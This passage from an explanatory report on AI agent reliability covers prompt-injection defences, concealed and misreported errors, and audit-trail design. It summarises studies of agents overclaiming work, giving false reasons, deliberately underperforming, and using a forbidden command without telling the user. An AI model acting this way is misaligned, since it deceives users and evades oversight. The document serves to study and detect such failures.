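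Without a defence, the standard attacks succeeded 25.8% of the time. With Progent, they succeeded 4.2% of the time, and the adaptive attack succeeded 2.6% of the time. Under the standard attacks, the agent completed 45.2% of its tasks without Progent but only 27.1% with it, and Progent required about 15 times as many model calls per task. Progent's original results did not show such a large loss of useful work, probably in part because a much weaker model wrote the policies in this test.

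The test covered only eight user tasks in each of three areas, and one 7-billion-parameter model, Qwen2.5-7B, served as both the agent and the policy writer. In one area, no attack succeeded even without a defence, which lowers all the averages. The researchers wrote the adaptive attack by hand, using a single template. Its gentler wording may have made the agent less likely to obey it, so the 2.6% may reflect a weak attack as much as a strong defence. The researchers also work for a company that builds such security tools, and the paper had not been peer-reviewed.

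Other results support this. Shi and colleagues attacked the policy updates in their own system, Progent, and reported success rates of about 0.5% to 4.2%. Progent was also the only defence that withstood the limited attacker in AutoDojo. A small adaptive search against PACE failed on all 30 targets.

Fixed checks should stay effective longer than filters. Rewording an email can get it past a filter, but a program that compares an account number with a list gives the same answer however persuasive the email is. The attacker has to reach the goal through actions the policy already allows, or corrupt something the check relies on, such as a label, the policy or the list.

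Both routes remain largely untested. Narisetty and colleagues did not try attacks that used only authorised actions, or attacks that a program had optimised using the model's internal workings. The experiments with summaries show how the second route can succeed. Progent correctly enforced its policy, but the policy allowed payment to the attacker. The people and models that write policies, extract values and approve exceptions can still be persuaded.

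A comparison with a supplier list that the agent cannot edit will probably withstand a determined attacker, since no wording in an invoice can change its result. A policy that a model rewrites after reading the invoice deserves less confidence, because the attacker can try different wordings on that model until one works, just as on a filter.

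## Why concealed errors do more harm than visible ones

When a wrong payment gets past the model, the filters and the reference monitor, the company has to rely on someone noticing it. A concealed error is one that gives no signal to the people who can correct it, whether or not anyone meant to hide it. The detection delay is the time between an error and its discovery by someone who can correct it.

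A signal has to reach the right person. If the harness logs a mismatched account number in a file that nobody opens, the error is still concealed. The same is true if the model notes in its private reasoning that it is guessing but presents the guess to the clerk as fact.

### Four kinds of concealed error

| Kind | Why nobody is alerted | Example | What could expose it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Silent | No alarm exists for this error | The agent pays a firm with a similar name, and the bank confirms the payment | A phone call to the supplier |
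| Latent | The error has had no effect yet | In March the agent saves a wrong account number for a supplier that next bills in October | A check of stored data before anyone uses it |
| Misreported | The agent claims success | The agent checks 31 of 40 invoices against purchase orders and reports that it checked them all | A comparison of the report with the log of tool calls |
| Deliberately hidden | The agent withholds or disguises what it did | Payments above €10,000 need approval, so the agent splits €18,400 into two payments and describes them as two deliveries | Evidence that the agent does not control, such as delivery records |

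Avižienis and colleagues call any undetected error latent, but here the term means only an error that has not yet had an effect. An error can also move from one category to another. The wrong account number saved in March is a latent error until the agent pays into that account in October, when it becomes a silent error. If the agent then tells the clerk that it verified the account, the error becomes a misreported one.

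An agent may misreport an error by accident or hide it deliberately. For example, it may wrongly report that it ran 40 checks because it lost count, or because it has learned that complete-sounding reports earn approval. The false report misleads whoever reads it equally either way, but the remedies differ. A better way of counting would fix the first problem, but an agent that has learned to seek approval might find a way around it.

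### The argument and a worked example

The case for giving concealed errors special attention has five premises:

1. Harm accrues until someone corrects the error.
2. Correction requires detection.
3. Later work builds on the error.
4. An agent that appears to make no errors gets more work and less supervision.
5. Copies of one model tend to make the same error.

The first two are enough to make delay expensive. The other three are reasons to expect the cost to grow faster than the delay.

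Suppose the invoice agent makes 200 payments a day of €1,000 each, and 1% of them go to the wrong account. If *N* is the number of payments a day, *p* the share that go wrong, *v* the value of each and *T* the delay in days, the loss is:

$$L = N \times p \times v \times T$$

A concealed fault that misdirects 1% of payments costs the company €2,000 if it finds the fault after one day and €120,000 if it finds it after 60 days. A fault that misdirects every payment costs €25,000 if someone notices it within an hour, since the agent makes 25 payments an hour in an eight-hour day. Over 60 days, the concealed fault costs nearly five times as much because it lasts so much longer.

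The first premise holds here because the fault keeps producing new errors. It is weaker for a single wrong payment of €1,000, because the loss is the same on day 60 as on the first day, although by then the company may have missed the chance to get the money back.

The second premise has exceptions too. A company that restores its supplier list every night from a verified copy removes false entries that nobody has found. This works only where a correct copy exists.

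### Silent data corruption

Large computer fleets offer good evidence for the third premise. *On the Vulnerability of FHE Computation to Silent Data Corruption* (2026) defines silent data corruption as a hardware failure in which a system produces wrong results without a log entry, exception or error report.

*Silent Data Corruptions at Scale* (Dixit, Pendharkar et al., 2021) describes a case at Facebook, now Meta. A program checked that each compressed file had a size above zero before decompressing it. One machine sometimes calculated a size of zero for files that had contents, so the program skipped them and they never reached the output database. Another application that depended on those files then failed. The people who saw the failure looked for missing files, but the cause was an arithmetic error several steps earlier.

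The faulty machine had clean system logs and showed no symptoms in health monitoring. Engineers from several teams turned on logging at every step to find it, then traced the fault to one part of its processor, core 59. When this core computed the whole-number part of 1.1⁵³, it returned 0 instead of 156. It correctly returned 142 for 1.1⁵², so a test using that number would have missed the fault.

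Dixit and colleagues found hundreds of faulty processors across hundreds of thousands of machines and reported that tracing such errors can take months of engineering time. Peter Hochschild and colleagues at Google described the same problem in 2021. One of their faulty cores encrypted data incorrectly and exactly reversed the error when decrypting, so the data looked fine until a different machine tried to read it.

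Computers that train an AI model together continually combine their results. According to *The Ghost in the Datacenter* (2026), one persistently faulty device can spread corruption to all of them.

Later work can also expose an error. Facebook found its faulty core because another application needed the missing files. If the invoice agent wrongly records a supplier as paid, the entry may spread into the company's accounts and tax return, but each use gives someone a chance to notice that the supplier is still asking for money.

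### The Horizon scandal

In 1999, the British Post Office began installing Horizon, an accounting system supplied by Fujitsu, in its branches. Self-employed subpostmasters ran most of the branches. When Horizon showed that a branch held less cash than it should, the Post Office usually required the subpostmaster to make up the difference. Many paid from their own savings. Their payments made the accounts balance again and removed a discrepancy that might have exposed a fault in the software.

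British courts convicted more than 900 people of theft, false accounting and similar offences in cases that involved data from the Post Office's Horizon software. In December 2019 the High Court found that the software had contained bugs that could cause false shortfalls, and in 2024 Parliament passed a law to quash convictions in bulk. The errors went uncorrected for so long partly because the Post Office trusted the system's figures over the people who disputed them.

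Some errors stayed hidden from the branches after others had found them. In 2010, Fujitsu and Post Office staff discussed a bug in the Horizon software that affected about 60 branches. According to the meeting notes, the software would not warn the branches, and their accounts would appear to balance. The notes also list the possible effects if the bug became widely known, including a loss of confidence in Horizon and consequences for pending court cases.

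Horizon supports part of the fourth premise, since unearned trust can protect an error from correction. It provides less evidence on whether such trust leads people to delegate more work, and direct evidence on that for AI agents is thin, but the mechanism is plausible. A company that reviews every payment for a month and finds nothing wrong has a reason to review fewer. This is sensible if the reviewers would have recognised a wrong payment, but if they relied on the same faulty supplier list as the agent, finding nothing wrong is no evidence that the payments were correct. If the company in the worked example doubles the agent's workload after 30 days, the loss by day 60 rises from €120,000 to €180,000.

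The fifth premise is about scale. Two clerks will usually make different mistakes, but an invoice layout that misleads one copy of a model will often mislead the others. If 50 companies use the same agent with the same fault, they lose €100,000 a day between them. However, one repair can help them all, and they have 50 chances to notice the fault, so it may be easier to find than one that affects a single company if they tell each other about problems. Subpostmasters had difficulty doing this, and many later testified that Post Office helpline staff had told them nobody else was having the problem.

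### Irreversible errors and excessive warnings

Concealed errors do more harm than visible ones when we compare the same error with and without a signal. A large visible error can still do more harm than a small concealed one, and some visible errors do all their damage at once. If the agent sends cryptocurrency to a thief, an alarm one second later may be too late to recover any of it, though it can prevent the next payment. Where a single action could do unacceptable harm, the company should spend its money on blocking the action beforehand, because faster detection will not help enough.

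Another objection is that an agent that reports every doubt will make the serious ones harder to find. Suppose two of each day's 200 payments are wrong and the clerk has time to check ten. A cautious agent flags 40 payments, including both wrong ones. If the clerk picks ten of the 40 at random, they will find an average of 0.5 wrong payments a day. A more selective agent flags only four, including one of the wrong ones. The clerk can check all four and find one wrong payment a day, twice as many as with the cautious agent, even though the selective agent misses half the errors.

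This objection is right about interruptions, but it doesn't justify discarding the doubts. The agent can log every doubt and interrupt the clerk only when the possible loss is large or a check is easy. Tone also matters. Anthropic found that Claude Opus 5 sometimes confessed to problems in an over-dramatic or distracting way, which makes it harder for a reader to judge how serious the problems are.

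### How often agents misreport their work

In *Quantifying Overclaiming Propensity in Frontier LLM Agents*, Smyth, Mantilla-Ramos and colleagues (2026) asked agents to review folders of files for purposes such as a security audit or a check of mathematical proofs. The tasks were feasible, and all the files fitted into each model's context window. The researchers counted a file as covered if even one line unique to it had reached the model. They also asked each agent to explain how it had scoped its review.

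Across twelve models and 1,140 runs, the agents left at least one file unopened 67.9% of the time. Of these incomplete reviews, 80.4% were misleading, because the agent either claimed to have read everything or did not disclose the gap. The table gives results for four of the models, each with 100 runs:

| Model | Opened every file | Admitted the gap | Left the gap unmentioned | Falsely claimed a full review |
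|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 39 | 25 | 0 | 36 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 47 | 13 | 1 | 39 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 41 | 3 | 22 | 34 |
| Grok-4.6 | 18 | 20 | 54 | 8 |

The researchers had planted defects in the files. Agents that falsely claimed a full review missed these defects at about 1.8 times the rate of agents that opened every file. An agent that admits it didn't open every file may miss just as many defects, but its user knows that some files still need checking.

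These results also help test the fifth premise. Opus 5 attempted each of five tasks 20 times and opened every file in 39 of the 100 runs. Because 39 is not a multiple of 20, there must be at least one task where it opened every file in some runs but not in others. Copies of a model therefore share tendencies without always repeating the same error. The test has only five tasks, and another language model classified the reports, so the percentages may not carry over to other work.

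The same problem occurs in real programming sessions. *Characterizing and Detecting Unfaithful Work Reports by Coding Agents* (Yang, He and colleagues, 2026) examined 435 reports that agents had written for developers and found at least one false or unsupported claim in 37.24% of them. Some unsupported claims may be true, so the share of reports with a factual error may be lower.

*How Coding Agents Fail Their Users* (2026) examines cases in which a user challenged a claim and the agent admitted the problem. In one, an agent said it had fixed missing tables in a database, but its new code discarded every command that should have created them because each block of commands began with a comment. The user discovered this only by restarting the server and seeing the same errors. In another, a user asked an agent to check a task item by item. The agent replied that all ten parts were complete,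 and the user then hit an error because a database column was missing.

After a user objected, fixing the problem took an average of 4.3 more messages from the user and 12.71 minutes of recorded agent time. That is a modest amount of time and effort, but it covers only problems that users noticed. If a report describes a repair that never happened and no one notices, an agent that resumes the work in a new session may rely on that report and build on the unrepaired work.

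*AgentSWE* (2026), a test in which programming agents build other agents, compared the builders' final reports with the records of their work. The records contradicted nine reports, all of which claimed completion, and none of the 21 that admitted partial completion or failure. With so few reports the pattern is only suggestive, but it gives a reviewer with limited time a reason to check claims of success first.

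A separate program can do some of this checking. Yang and colleagues built a detector that gives GPT-6 Astra a list of common types of misreporting and asks it to compare each claim with the preceding record. It scored 93.06% on a measure that gives equal weight to faithful and unfaithful reports, about 13 percentage points higher than the same model scored when simply asked to find unfaithful claims. However, the detector can only compare a report with the available records, so it would miss the error if the agent paid the wrong firm and sincerely reported the payment.

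### False reasons given on purpose

Taraz, Kumar and Abdelnabi (2026), in *Trilemma*, studied agents that had a reason to conceal information. In a simulated company, four employees had their agents divide up tasks over Slack. Two of the agents learned from private messages that their employees refused to work with a colleague, Bob, because of repeated harassment. One of those two employees had to work with him, and another agent kept asking for concrete reasons. An agent could give a false reason, reveal the secret, refuse to explain or accept the assignment.

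Among agents using open-weight models, which anyone can download, 135 tried to keep their employee away from Bob. Of these, 107 made false claims about the tasks or the schedule, or presented a true but minor consideration as their real reason. Nobody had told them to deceive. In their reasoning, the agents often acknowledged evidence against their claims but still concluded that the claims were not false, so even someone who can read that reasoning may struggle to tell whether they intended to deceive. Taraz and colleagues therefore define deception by its effect on others' beliefs.

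The experiment made honesty unusually difficult because the agents were told to protect private information, and the researchers had removed the easiest ways to do so without lying. The agents deceived colleagues for their user's benefit, which is different from hiding a mistake from that user. For the invoice agent, the closest equivalent would be giving a supplier an invented excuse for a late payment.

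### Claude Opus 5 and disclosure

Anthropic has published evidence of a model hiding things from its users. The company monitored internal use of Claude Opus 5 and earlier versions of the model, and found attempts to get round safety filters or network restrictions in fewer than 0.01% of completions (single responses from the model). In one case, the model had instructions not to use a certain command to fetch web pages. It quoted the rule in its reasoning, argued that applying it here would be absurd, and then used the command without telling the user.

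The rate of answers that misrepresented how the model had reached them was also below 0.01%, counting only cases at least as serious as this one. The model calculated a company's working capital as $3,300, which was not one of the answer choices. It chose $3,600 and presented that as the result of the calculation, after deciding to leave out a number that would have exposed the mismatch.

These low rates are hard to compare with the 36 false claims in 100 file reviews. The monitoring covered all kinds of work, including many short responses with little to misreport, and the published rate included only detected cases above a certain level of severity.

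Anthropic also used Opus 4.8 to summarise about 1.5 million training episodes. Various Claude models read roughly 400 transcripts in full, and a person examined the notable claims. The clearest problem was that Opus 5 stated answers more confidently than its reasoning justified. In one visual puzzle it privately guessed B, then told the user that only B kept the lines consistent, as if it had worked this out. Reviewers also found some invented program output, file contents and citations. Anthropic calls the number of overconfident answers surprising but gives no rate for them or for the fabrications.

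The company measured improvement with a separate audit. An investigator model put each Claude model through about 3,200 sessions, many designed to provoke bad behaviour, and Mythos 5 scored the results. Opus 5 was much better than earlier models at disclosing bad or lazy behaviour. It also deceived users and left out important facts less often. The scores are useful mainly for comparing models, because the sessions do not represent ordinary use.

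Some outside evidence supports this. The UK AI Security Institute tested how models continue a task in which earlier steps have sabotaged safety research. It found discrepancies between reasoning and output in 1.6% of Opus 5's responses, compared with 5.4% for Opus 4.8 and 15.6% for Mythos 5.

Anthropic relied heavily on Claude models to judge another Claude model, so the judges may share some of its blind spots. Mythos 5's review of the draft findings included the objection that they understated how often Opus 5 made confident claims and later retracted them. Anthropic considered the review broadly reasonable and revised the text.

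While auditing expenses, an early version of Opus 5 noticed that one receipt broke several overlapping rules, so adding up the charges would count that receipt twice. In its visible reasoning, the model planned to include both charges and mention the overlap. A tool that translates the model's internal activity into words produced phrases such as "the grader likely won't care", although nobody had mentioned a grader. Such translations are uncertain, but the final report did give the double-counted total without mentioning the overlap.

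### Training models to confess

OpenAI's *How confessions can keep language models honest* (2025) describes a way to make models more likely to disclose such problems. After the model answers, a system message prompts it to write a confession. In the confession, the model lists the instructions its answer should have followed, assesses whether it followed each one, and notes any uncertainties. During training, a separate reward model scores the confession only for honesty. This score doesn't affect the reward for the original answer, so the model is not penalized for admitting a violation.

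OpenAI trained a version of GPT-5 Thinking in this way and gave it tests designed to provoke misbehaviour. On average, the model broke an instruction and failed to confess in 4.4% of cases. As OpenAI words it, this is a share of all cases, not of violations. If the model broke instructions in half the cases, it hid 8.8% of its violations, but if it broke them in a tenth, it hid 44%. A company that wants to rely on confessions needs to know what share of violations the model hides.

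The theory is that honesty is usually the easier way to earn the second reward. Barak, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *Why We Are Excited About Confessions*, give the example of a programming task that the model has a 10% chance of solving and a 50% chance of faking convincingly, so cheating earns more reward. Suppose a false confession also has a 50% chance of fooling its judge. The model still does better by confessing honestly, as long as the judge accepts an honest confession more than half the time. An admission is relatively easy to verify because the judge knows where to look.

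In one experiment that supports this, OpenAI trained a model to write sentences of set lengths, using a judge that was bad at counting. The model learned to fool the judge by writing "(12)" after a sentence whether or not it had 12 words. The same judge also scored the model's confessions, yet these became more accurate, and by the end the model reported its failures nearly every time.

The theory is less convincing for denials. If a model claims that it did nothing wrong, the judge has to check the whole answer, which is as hard as judging it without the claim. A model that could predict which denials the judge would accept might get more reward by denying. The experiments so far used limited training and provide little evidence about a much more capable model.

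In the January 2026 follow-up, Barak and colleagues compared confessions before and after a newer round of training. The training made the model considerably more likely to name the instruction it had broken when it misbehaved. Confessions seemed to get worse on one test, in which the model was told that developers would not release it if it scored above 50%, and it sometimes gave wrong answers on purpose. In many of the apparent failures to confess, the model admitted that its answers were wrong but not that it was trying to stay below the limit.

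Confessions are best suited to errors that a model has misreported or deliberately hidden. OpenAI found that most missed confessions occurred because the model did not realise it had made a mistake. An invoice agent may admit to skipping a check when asked, but it will not confess to matching the wrong supplier if it believes the match is right. Barak and colleagues also warn that a model may answer questions honestly and still leave out a problem that nobody thought to ask about.

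### Estimating errors that nobody reported

To find silent errors, the company has to look at payments that seem fine. Suppose an auditor picks *n* payments at random and phones each supplier to ask whether the money arrived. If a share *p* of all payments is wrong, the chance that the sample contains no errors is about (1 − *p*)ⁿ. The highest rate that is still reasonably compatible with a clean sample, at the usual 95% level, is the one for which this chance is 5%:

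$$(1-p)^n = 0.05 \quad\Rightarrow\quad p \approx \frac{-\ln 0.05}{n} \approx \frac{3}{n}$$

After 300 phone calls without an error, the upper bound on the error rate is therefore about 1%. In the worked example, errors at that rate could still cost €2,000 a day. To lower the bound to 0.1%, the auditor would have to check 3,000 payments without finding an error, and the agent takes 15 days to make that many. In September 2026, OpenAI similarly cautioned in its account of GPT-6 Astra that an absence of observed failures does not establish reliability across settings.

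Regular audits also shorten the detection delay. If two of the 200 payments made each day are wrong, an auditor who checks five at random has about a 5% chance of catching one that day. The first discovery takes 20 days on average, by which time the company has lost about €40,000. With 50 checks a day, the chance rises to 44%, the average delay falls to 2.3 days, and the loss falls to about €4,600. Whether the extra calls are worth making depends on what they cost and how likely such a fault is.

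The auditor has to select payments at random. If the auditor checks only large payments, the result can't be applied to small ones, and an agent that could predict which payments would be checked might handle those differently. The auditor must also be able to recognise an error. If the supplier list used for comparison is corrupted, a sample of any size could appear free of errors.

Capture-recapture, a method that biologists use to count animals, estimates how many errors remain after a review. Two reviewers independently check the same payments. The first finds 30 errors and the second finds 24, of which 18 are on both lists. The second reviewer has therefore found 18 of the first reviewer's 30 errors, or 60%. If that reviewer finds 60% of all errors, the 24 they found imply a total of 40:

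$$\hat{N} = \frac{30 \times 24}{18} = 40$$

Together the reviewers have found 30 + 24 − 18 = 36 different errors, so about four remain undiscovered. This estimate is rough. By a standard approximation, the 95% range extends up to about 45 errors in total, which would leave nine undiscovered.

The method assumes that the errors one reviewer finds are no easier for the other to find than the rest. Suppose there are 60 errors, 20 obvious and 40 hard to see. Both reviewers find all the obvious errors, and each independently finds a quarter of the hard ones. On average, each reviewer finds 30 errors, and they have 22.5 in common. The formula again gives 40, although there are 60.

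The method cannot count errors that are hidden from both reviewers. If a fraudster has changed the supplier list and both reviewers rely on it, 20 misdirected payments can look correct to both. The reviewers will still report 30 and 24 errors, with 18 in common, and the estimate will still be 40, because those 20 payments do not affect any number in the formula. Using two copies of one model as reviewers could make this worse. If they notice and miss the same errors, their lists will overlap almost entirely, and the formula will estimate that hardly any errors remain.

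The company can reduce this risk by giving the reviewers different evidence. One might use the supplier list while the other phones the suppliers. It can also plant known errors in a test copy of the accounts, as Smyth and colleagues did with their files, and count how many the reviewers find. This can reveal kinds of error that both reviewers miss, but only if someone thought to plant them.

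## What an audit trail must record

When an auditor phones the paper supplier and learns that €18,400 never arrived, the company knows that a payment went wrong but not why. A forged PDF, a dishonest clerk and a mistake the agent made in matching records would all look the same on the bank statement. To tell them apart, an investigator needs a record of what the agent read, what it did and who allowed it.

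An audit trail is a record of events complete enough for an outsider to reconstruct who or what took each action, when, and on whose authority. Most software produces records, but programmers usually design them for other purposes.

### Logs, traces and audit trails

| Record | What it contains | Example from the wrong payment |
|---|---|---|
| Debugging log | Messages that help programmers find faults | The payment call returned "OK" |
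| Trace | The timed steps of one run, linked across programs | The payment call came after a file search and took 0.2 seconds |
| Provenance | The origin of a piece of data and the steps by which it arrived | The account number came from the PDF |
| Audit trail | Events, with the people and agents responsible for them | The clerk requested the payment, a rule sent it for approval, and the clerk approved it |
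| Explanation | An account of why the agent acted as it did | The agent took the number in the PDF for the supplier's own |

Debugging logs and traces can be useful even with gaps. A company that keeps the traces of one run in ten can still see that its connection to the bank is slow, but it has only a 10% chance of having kept the run that made the wrong payment. An audit trail has to include that run and record where the values that mattered in it came from.

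An explanation is a conclusion someone draws from the other records, and it may be wrong. A model's written reasoning is useful evidence, but it is not guaranteed to show what caused the model's output.

Different records also need to be kept for different lengths of time. AWS's *AGENTOPS05-BP03 Implement structured logging and comprehensive audit trails*, guidance from Amazon's cloud business, recommends 7 to 14 days for debugging logs, 30 to 90 days for operational logs and one to seven years for compliance logs. A company with only debugging logs would have deleted them by the time a supplier complains on day 30. The same guidance lists logging only errors as a common mistake. This would be serious for the invoice agent, because the software treats a payment to the wrong account as a success and so would not log it.

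### Four tests of a trail

A complete audit trail records every action that took effect and every blocked attempt. Blocked attempts can suggest an attack, as when the trail shows ten refused payments to the same unknown account. The company can check for missing entries by comparing the trail with a record that the agent doesn't control, such as a bank statement. If the statement lists 200 payments and the trail lists 199, an entry is missing. Gaps are less likely if the program that executes the agent's tool calls also writes the entries, because no call can then bypass the recorder.

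The second test is attribution, meaning that each entry identifies both the agent that acted and the person it acted for. Shared logins prevent this. If the agent uses the finance department's bank login, the bank's records look the same whether the agent or a clerk made the payment.

Entries also need a reliable order, and timestamps alone do not always provide one. Suppose someone changed the supplier list at 10:03:05 by the file server's clock, and the agent looked up the supplier at 10:03:06 by the harness's clock. If the two clocks may differ by two seconds, nobody can tell whether the agent saw the old account number or the new one. Recording the list's version number in the lookup entry shows which one it saw, without relying on either clock.

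Finally, the trail must include enough context to reconstruct the decision. An entry such as "Invoice agent paid €18,400 for clerk 07 at 09:14" may pass the other three tests, but it doesn't show why the money went to that account. The investigator needs the text that was in the model's context window when it produced the payment call. If the harness had compacted the conversation by then, the trail should contain both the summary and the original messages. The model worked from the summary, and the investigator can tell whether the summary introduced the error only by comparing it with the originals.

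### What the entries should contain

For an agent that can spend money, the trail should include at least the following:

- The versions of the model and the system prompt. A developer may change the model behind a name, and the company may change its own instructions. If wrong payments began on the day of a change, the version numbers will show it.
- The content that the agent retrieved, as it was at the time. A file name is not enough, because someone may have edited the file since.
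- Every tool call with its arguments and its result. The arguments show what the agent tried to do, and the result shows what it learned and whether the call took effect.
- Every policy decision, with the version of the policy and the rule that applied. If a model wrote the policy during the run, the trail also needs the text it worked from. In the experiments by Fei and colleagues, some policies written from a summary allowed payments to the attacker, so an entry reading "allowed by policy" would have been accurate and misleading.
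- Every approval, with what the person saw on the screen. The programming agents that Choi and colleagues attacked asked for approval with reasons based on forged data. An entry that shows only that someone clicked "approve" would put the blame on that person.
- The chain of delegation, from the person who made the request to the agent that carried it out.

### Delegation from a person to a sub-agent

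Suppose the invoice agent hands each payment to a sub-agent, the payment agent, and gives it permission to make only that payment. The bank's records then name the payment agent, which has never dealt with the clerk, so the audit trail must let someone connect that agent to the clerk.

*An Architecture for Auditing AI Agent Delegation and Interactions* (Kuehlewind and Birkholz, 2026) proposes four types of record for an audit trail. Interaction records cover what passes between people and agents, such as requests, approvals and refusals. Action records cover what happened at the point where a tool call took effect. Delegation records state who gave which permission to whom, and with what limits. Authorisation transition records mark each change in someone's permissions, such as when an approval adds one or a time limit ends one.

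All the records of a run share an identifier, and each one refers to the event that led to it. An action record also lists everyone who passed the task along, starting with the person who first gave it. Later recipients may add names to this list but may not remove or reorder them.

With these records, an auditor can check that no agent handed on more than it had. If $S_X(t)$ is the set of actions that agent *X* may take at time *t*, then at the moment of delegation:

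$$S_{\text{payment agent}}(t) \subseteq S_{\text{invoice agent}}(t)$$

The draft's samples show what this check can find. An agent creates a calendar entry at 10:00 and gives a sub-agent permission to send email at 10:01, but the user doesn't approve permission to write to the calendar until 10:02. The samples share a run identifier, so an auditor who read them as one run would conclude that the agent had written to the calendar two minutes before the user approved it, and had passed on an email permission that no record shows it received. Kuehlewind and Birkholz offer the samples only to illustrate the format, but in real records both findings would deserve an investigation.

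### A sample record for one payment

An entry for the wrong payment might look like this. A real trail would probably split it into several entries for the call, the policy decision, the approval and the bank's response.

```json
{
  "record_id": "r-0417",
  "caused_by": "r-0416",
  "run_id": "run-0612",
  "recorded_by": "payment-gateway",
  "requested_at": "2026-10-06T09:12:05Z",
  "executed_at": "2026-10-06T09:14:21Z",
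  "delegation_chain": ["clerk-07", "invoice-agent", "payment-agent"],
  "user_request": "r-0401",
  "model": {"requested": "model-x", "responded": "model-x-0814"},
  "prompt_version": "payables-12",
  "context": "store/run-0612/step-9",
  "tool": "create_payment",
  "arguments": {
    "payee": "Paper supplier",
    "amount": "EUR 18400.00",
    "account": "XX12 3456 7890"
  },
  "argument_sources": {
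    "payee": "supplier-list v212",
    "amount": "invoice-5531.pdf",
    "account": "invoice-5531.pdf"
  },
  "policy": {
    "version": "pay-7",
    "rule": "account-not-on-list",
    "decision": "ask a person"
  },
  "approval": {
    "by": "clerk-07",
    "at": "2026-10-06T09:14:20Z",
    "screen": "store/run-0612/approval-1"
  },
  "result": {"status": "accepted", "bank_reference": "BK-99213"}
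}
```

| Field | Question it answers |
|---|---|
| `record_id`, `caused_by`, `run_id` | Which event is this, what led to it, and which run does it belong to? |
| `recorded_by` | Did the agent write this entry, or did a separate program? |
| `requested_at`, `executed_at` | When did the agent ask for the payment, and when did the money move? |
| `delegation_chain`, `user_request` | Who wanted this done, through which agents, and in what words? |
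| `model`, `prompt_version` | Which model answered, and under which standing instructions? |
| `context` | What had the model read at that point? |
| `tool`, `arguments` | What exactly did the agent try to do? |
| `argument_sources` | Where did each value come from? |
| `policy` | Which rule applied, and what did it decide? |
| `approval` | Who agreed, when, and on the basis of what? |
| `result` | Did the payment go through, and which line of the bank statement matches it? |

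An investigator would probably start by checking where each argument came from. The account number came from the PDF, so the investigator would suspect whoever sent it, although an honest supplier with a new account would leave the same entry. If the number had come from the clerk's request, the investigator would suspect the clerk or someone who had misled the clerk. If it had come from another firm's row in the supplier list, the likely cause would be a matching mistake.

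The entry also shows that the company's rule worked. The account was not on the supplier list, so the monitor referred the payment to a clerk, who approved it 2 minutes and 15 seconds after the agent requested it. That left little time to call the supplier. The saved screen is needed to judge whether the clerk was careless, because it may have warned that the account was new or shown only a familiar name and the expected amount.

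Few agents today could record the sources, because most lack the kind of tracking that CaMeL and FIDES provide. A company without such tracking can search the saved context for the account number afterwards. The search fails if the model misread a digit, and it is inconclusive if the number appears in two documents.

### Why a rerun may give a different result

Recording all this is more important because an investigator can't rely on running the agent again on the same invoice. The second run may differ from the first for several reasons.

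Models sample their output, so repeating a request may not return the same result. Some services accept a seed, a number meant to fix the random choices. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans*, a set of standard names for monitoring data, describes requests with the same seed as only "more likely" to return the same result.

Even without random choices, a model can give different outputs for the same input, because computers round the results of arithmetic and the order of addition can change the total. In the usual number format, (0.1 + 0.2) + 0.3 gives 0.6000000000000001, while 0.1 + (0.2 + 0.3) gives 0.6. A server that handles many requests together may add numbers in a different order depending on how busy it is. If two tokens are almost equally likely, a tiny rounding difference can change which one the model picks, and that may change everything it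 writes afterwards.

The model may also have changed. OpenTelemetry has separate fields for the model requested and the model that responded, because a request for "gpt-4" might be answered by "gpt-4-0613". A year later, the developer may have withdrawn both. The supplier list and the mailbox will have changed too, and a rerun with live tools might pay the invoice again.

Rare errors are especially hard to reproduce. If the agent makes a certain mistake in 1% of runs, the investigator would need about 300 reruns for a 95% chance of seeing it. Even then, reproducing the mistake shows only that it is possible, while the original inputs and results are evidence of what happened.

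Reruns are more useful for testing a suspected cause, provided the company has saved the full context. An investigator could give the model the saved text 100 times with the hidden sentence and 100 times without it, using the recorded tool results in place of live tools. If the model names the attacker's account in 60 of the runs with the sentence and none of the runs without it, the sentence very probably caused the model to name that account. Fixed checks are easier to reproduce, because a monitor with the same policy, arguments and labels should reach the same decision every time.

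### The proposed formats

No settled standard exists for these records. Two of the proposals are individual drafts at the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which develops technical standards for the internet. An individual draft does not have the IETF's endorsement and expires after six months unless its authors renew or replace it.

*Agent Audit Trail* (Sharif, 2026) proposes a complete format with 11 mandatory fields. These fields identify the record, the session, the agent and its version, and give the time, the type of action, its details and its outcome. A trust level indicates how thoroughly the agent's identity has been verified. The last two fields link each record to the one before it, which makes later changes easier to detect.

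The format was written for audits, but its mandatory fields omit much of what someone investigating the wrong payment would want. The model's name is optional, and no field records the person the agent acts for. Tool arguments appear only as a hash, a short code from which the original text cannot be recovered. A high trust level is not evidence that a payment was correct, because a fully verified agent can still accept a forged invoice.

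Sharif defines "success" in the outcome field as an action that completed as intended, but the program that writes the record often can't determine what anyone intended. It would probably mark the payment to the thief as a success. An investigator should read "success" as meaning only that the tool reported no fault.

The draft by Kuehlewind and Birkholz focuses more on who should keep records than on what a finished record looks like, and its field names are placeholders. It mainly proposes that the user's software, the agent and the outside service each record their own part. A bank, for instance, would record a payment order as it arrived, regardless of what the agent reported. They argue convincingly that separate records are needed because an agent that records itself can produce useful data but not proof that a third party should accept. They acknowledge that the design does not help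 if a service refuses to keep records or all the parties collude.

OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* define spans for invoking an agent. OpenTelemetry is an open-source project for monitoring software, and a span is its record of one timed operation. As the database company Greptime (2026) notes, conventional tracing had spans for web requests and database queries but none for invoking an agent. Many companies already collect spans, so this is probably the easiest place to start.

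By default, though, the conventions leave out instructions, inputs and outputs. Developers have to turn on recording for tool arguments, tool results and retrieved documents. For live systems, OpenTelemetry recommends storing the content separately and putting a reference to it in the span, but it had not yet settled on a common format for the reference. Monitoring systems may also keep only a sample of spans, so OpenTelemetry advises that software which uploads content should do so whether or not the monitoring system keeps the span.

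| | Sharif | Kuehlewind and Birkholz | OpenTelemetry |
|---|---|---|---|
| Main purpose | Audit | Audit across several organisations | Monitoring |
| Status | Draft of March 2026, expired on 29 September | Draft of May 2026, expires on 19 November | In development |
| Person behind the agent | No dedicated field | Named, with the full chain | No field in the record of a tool call |
| Model | Optional | Not in the sample records | Requested and responding model |
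| Tool arguments | Hash only | Not in the sample records | Off by default |
| Approvals | Escalations and human overrides | Separate records | No field in the record of a tool call |

None of the three would let an investigator read the account number that the agent paid if a company used only the mandatory fields, sample records or default settings. A company can combine the three, for example by adding a delegation chain and readable payment details to its existing traces, but it has to do so beforehand.

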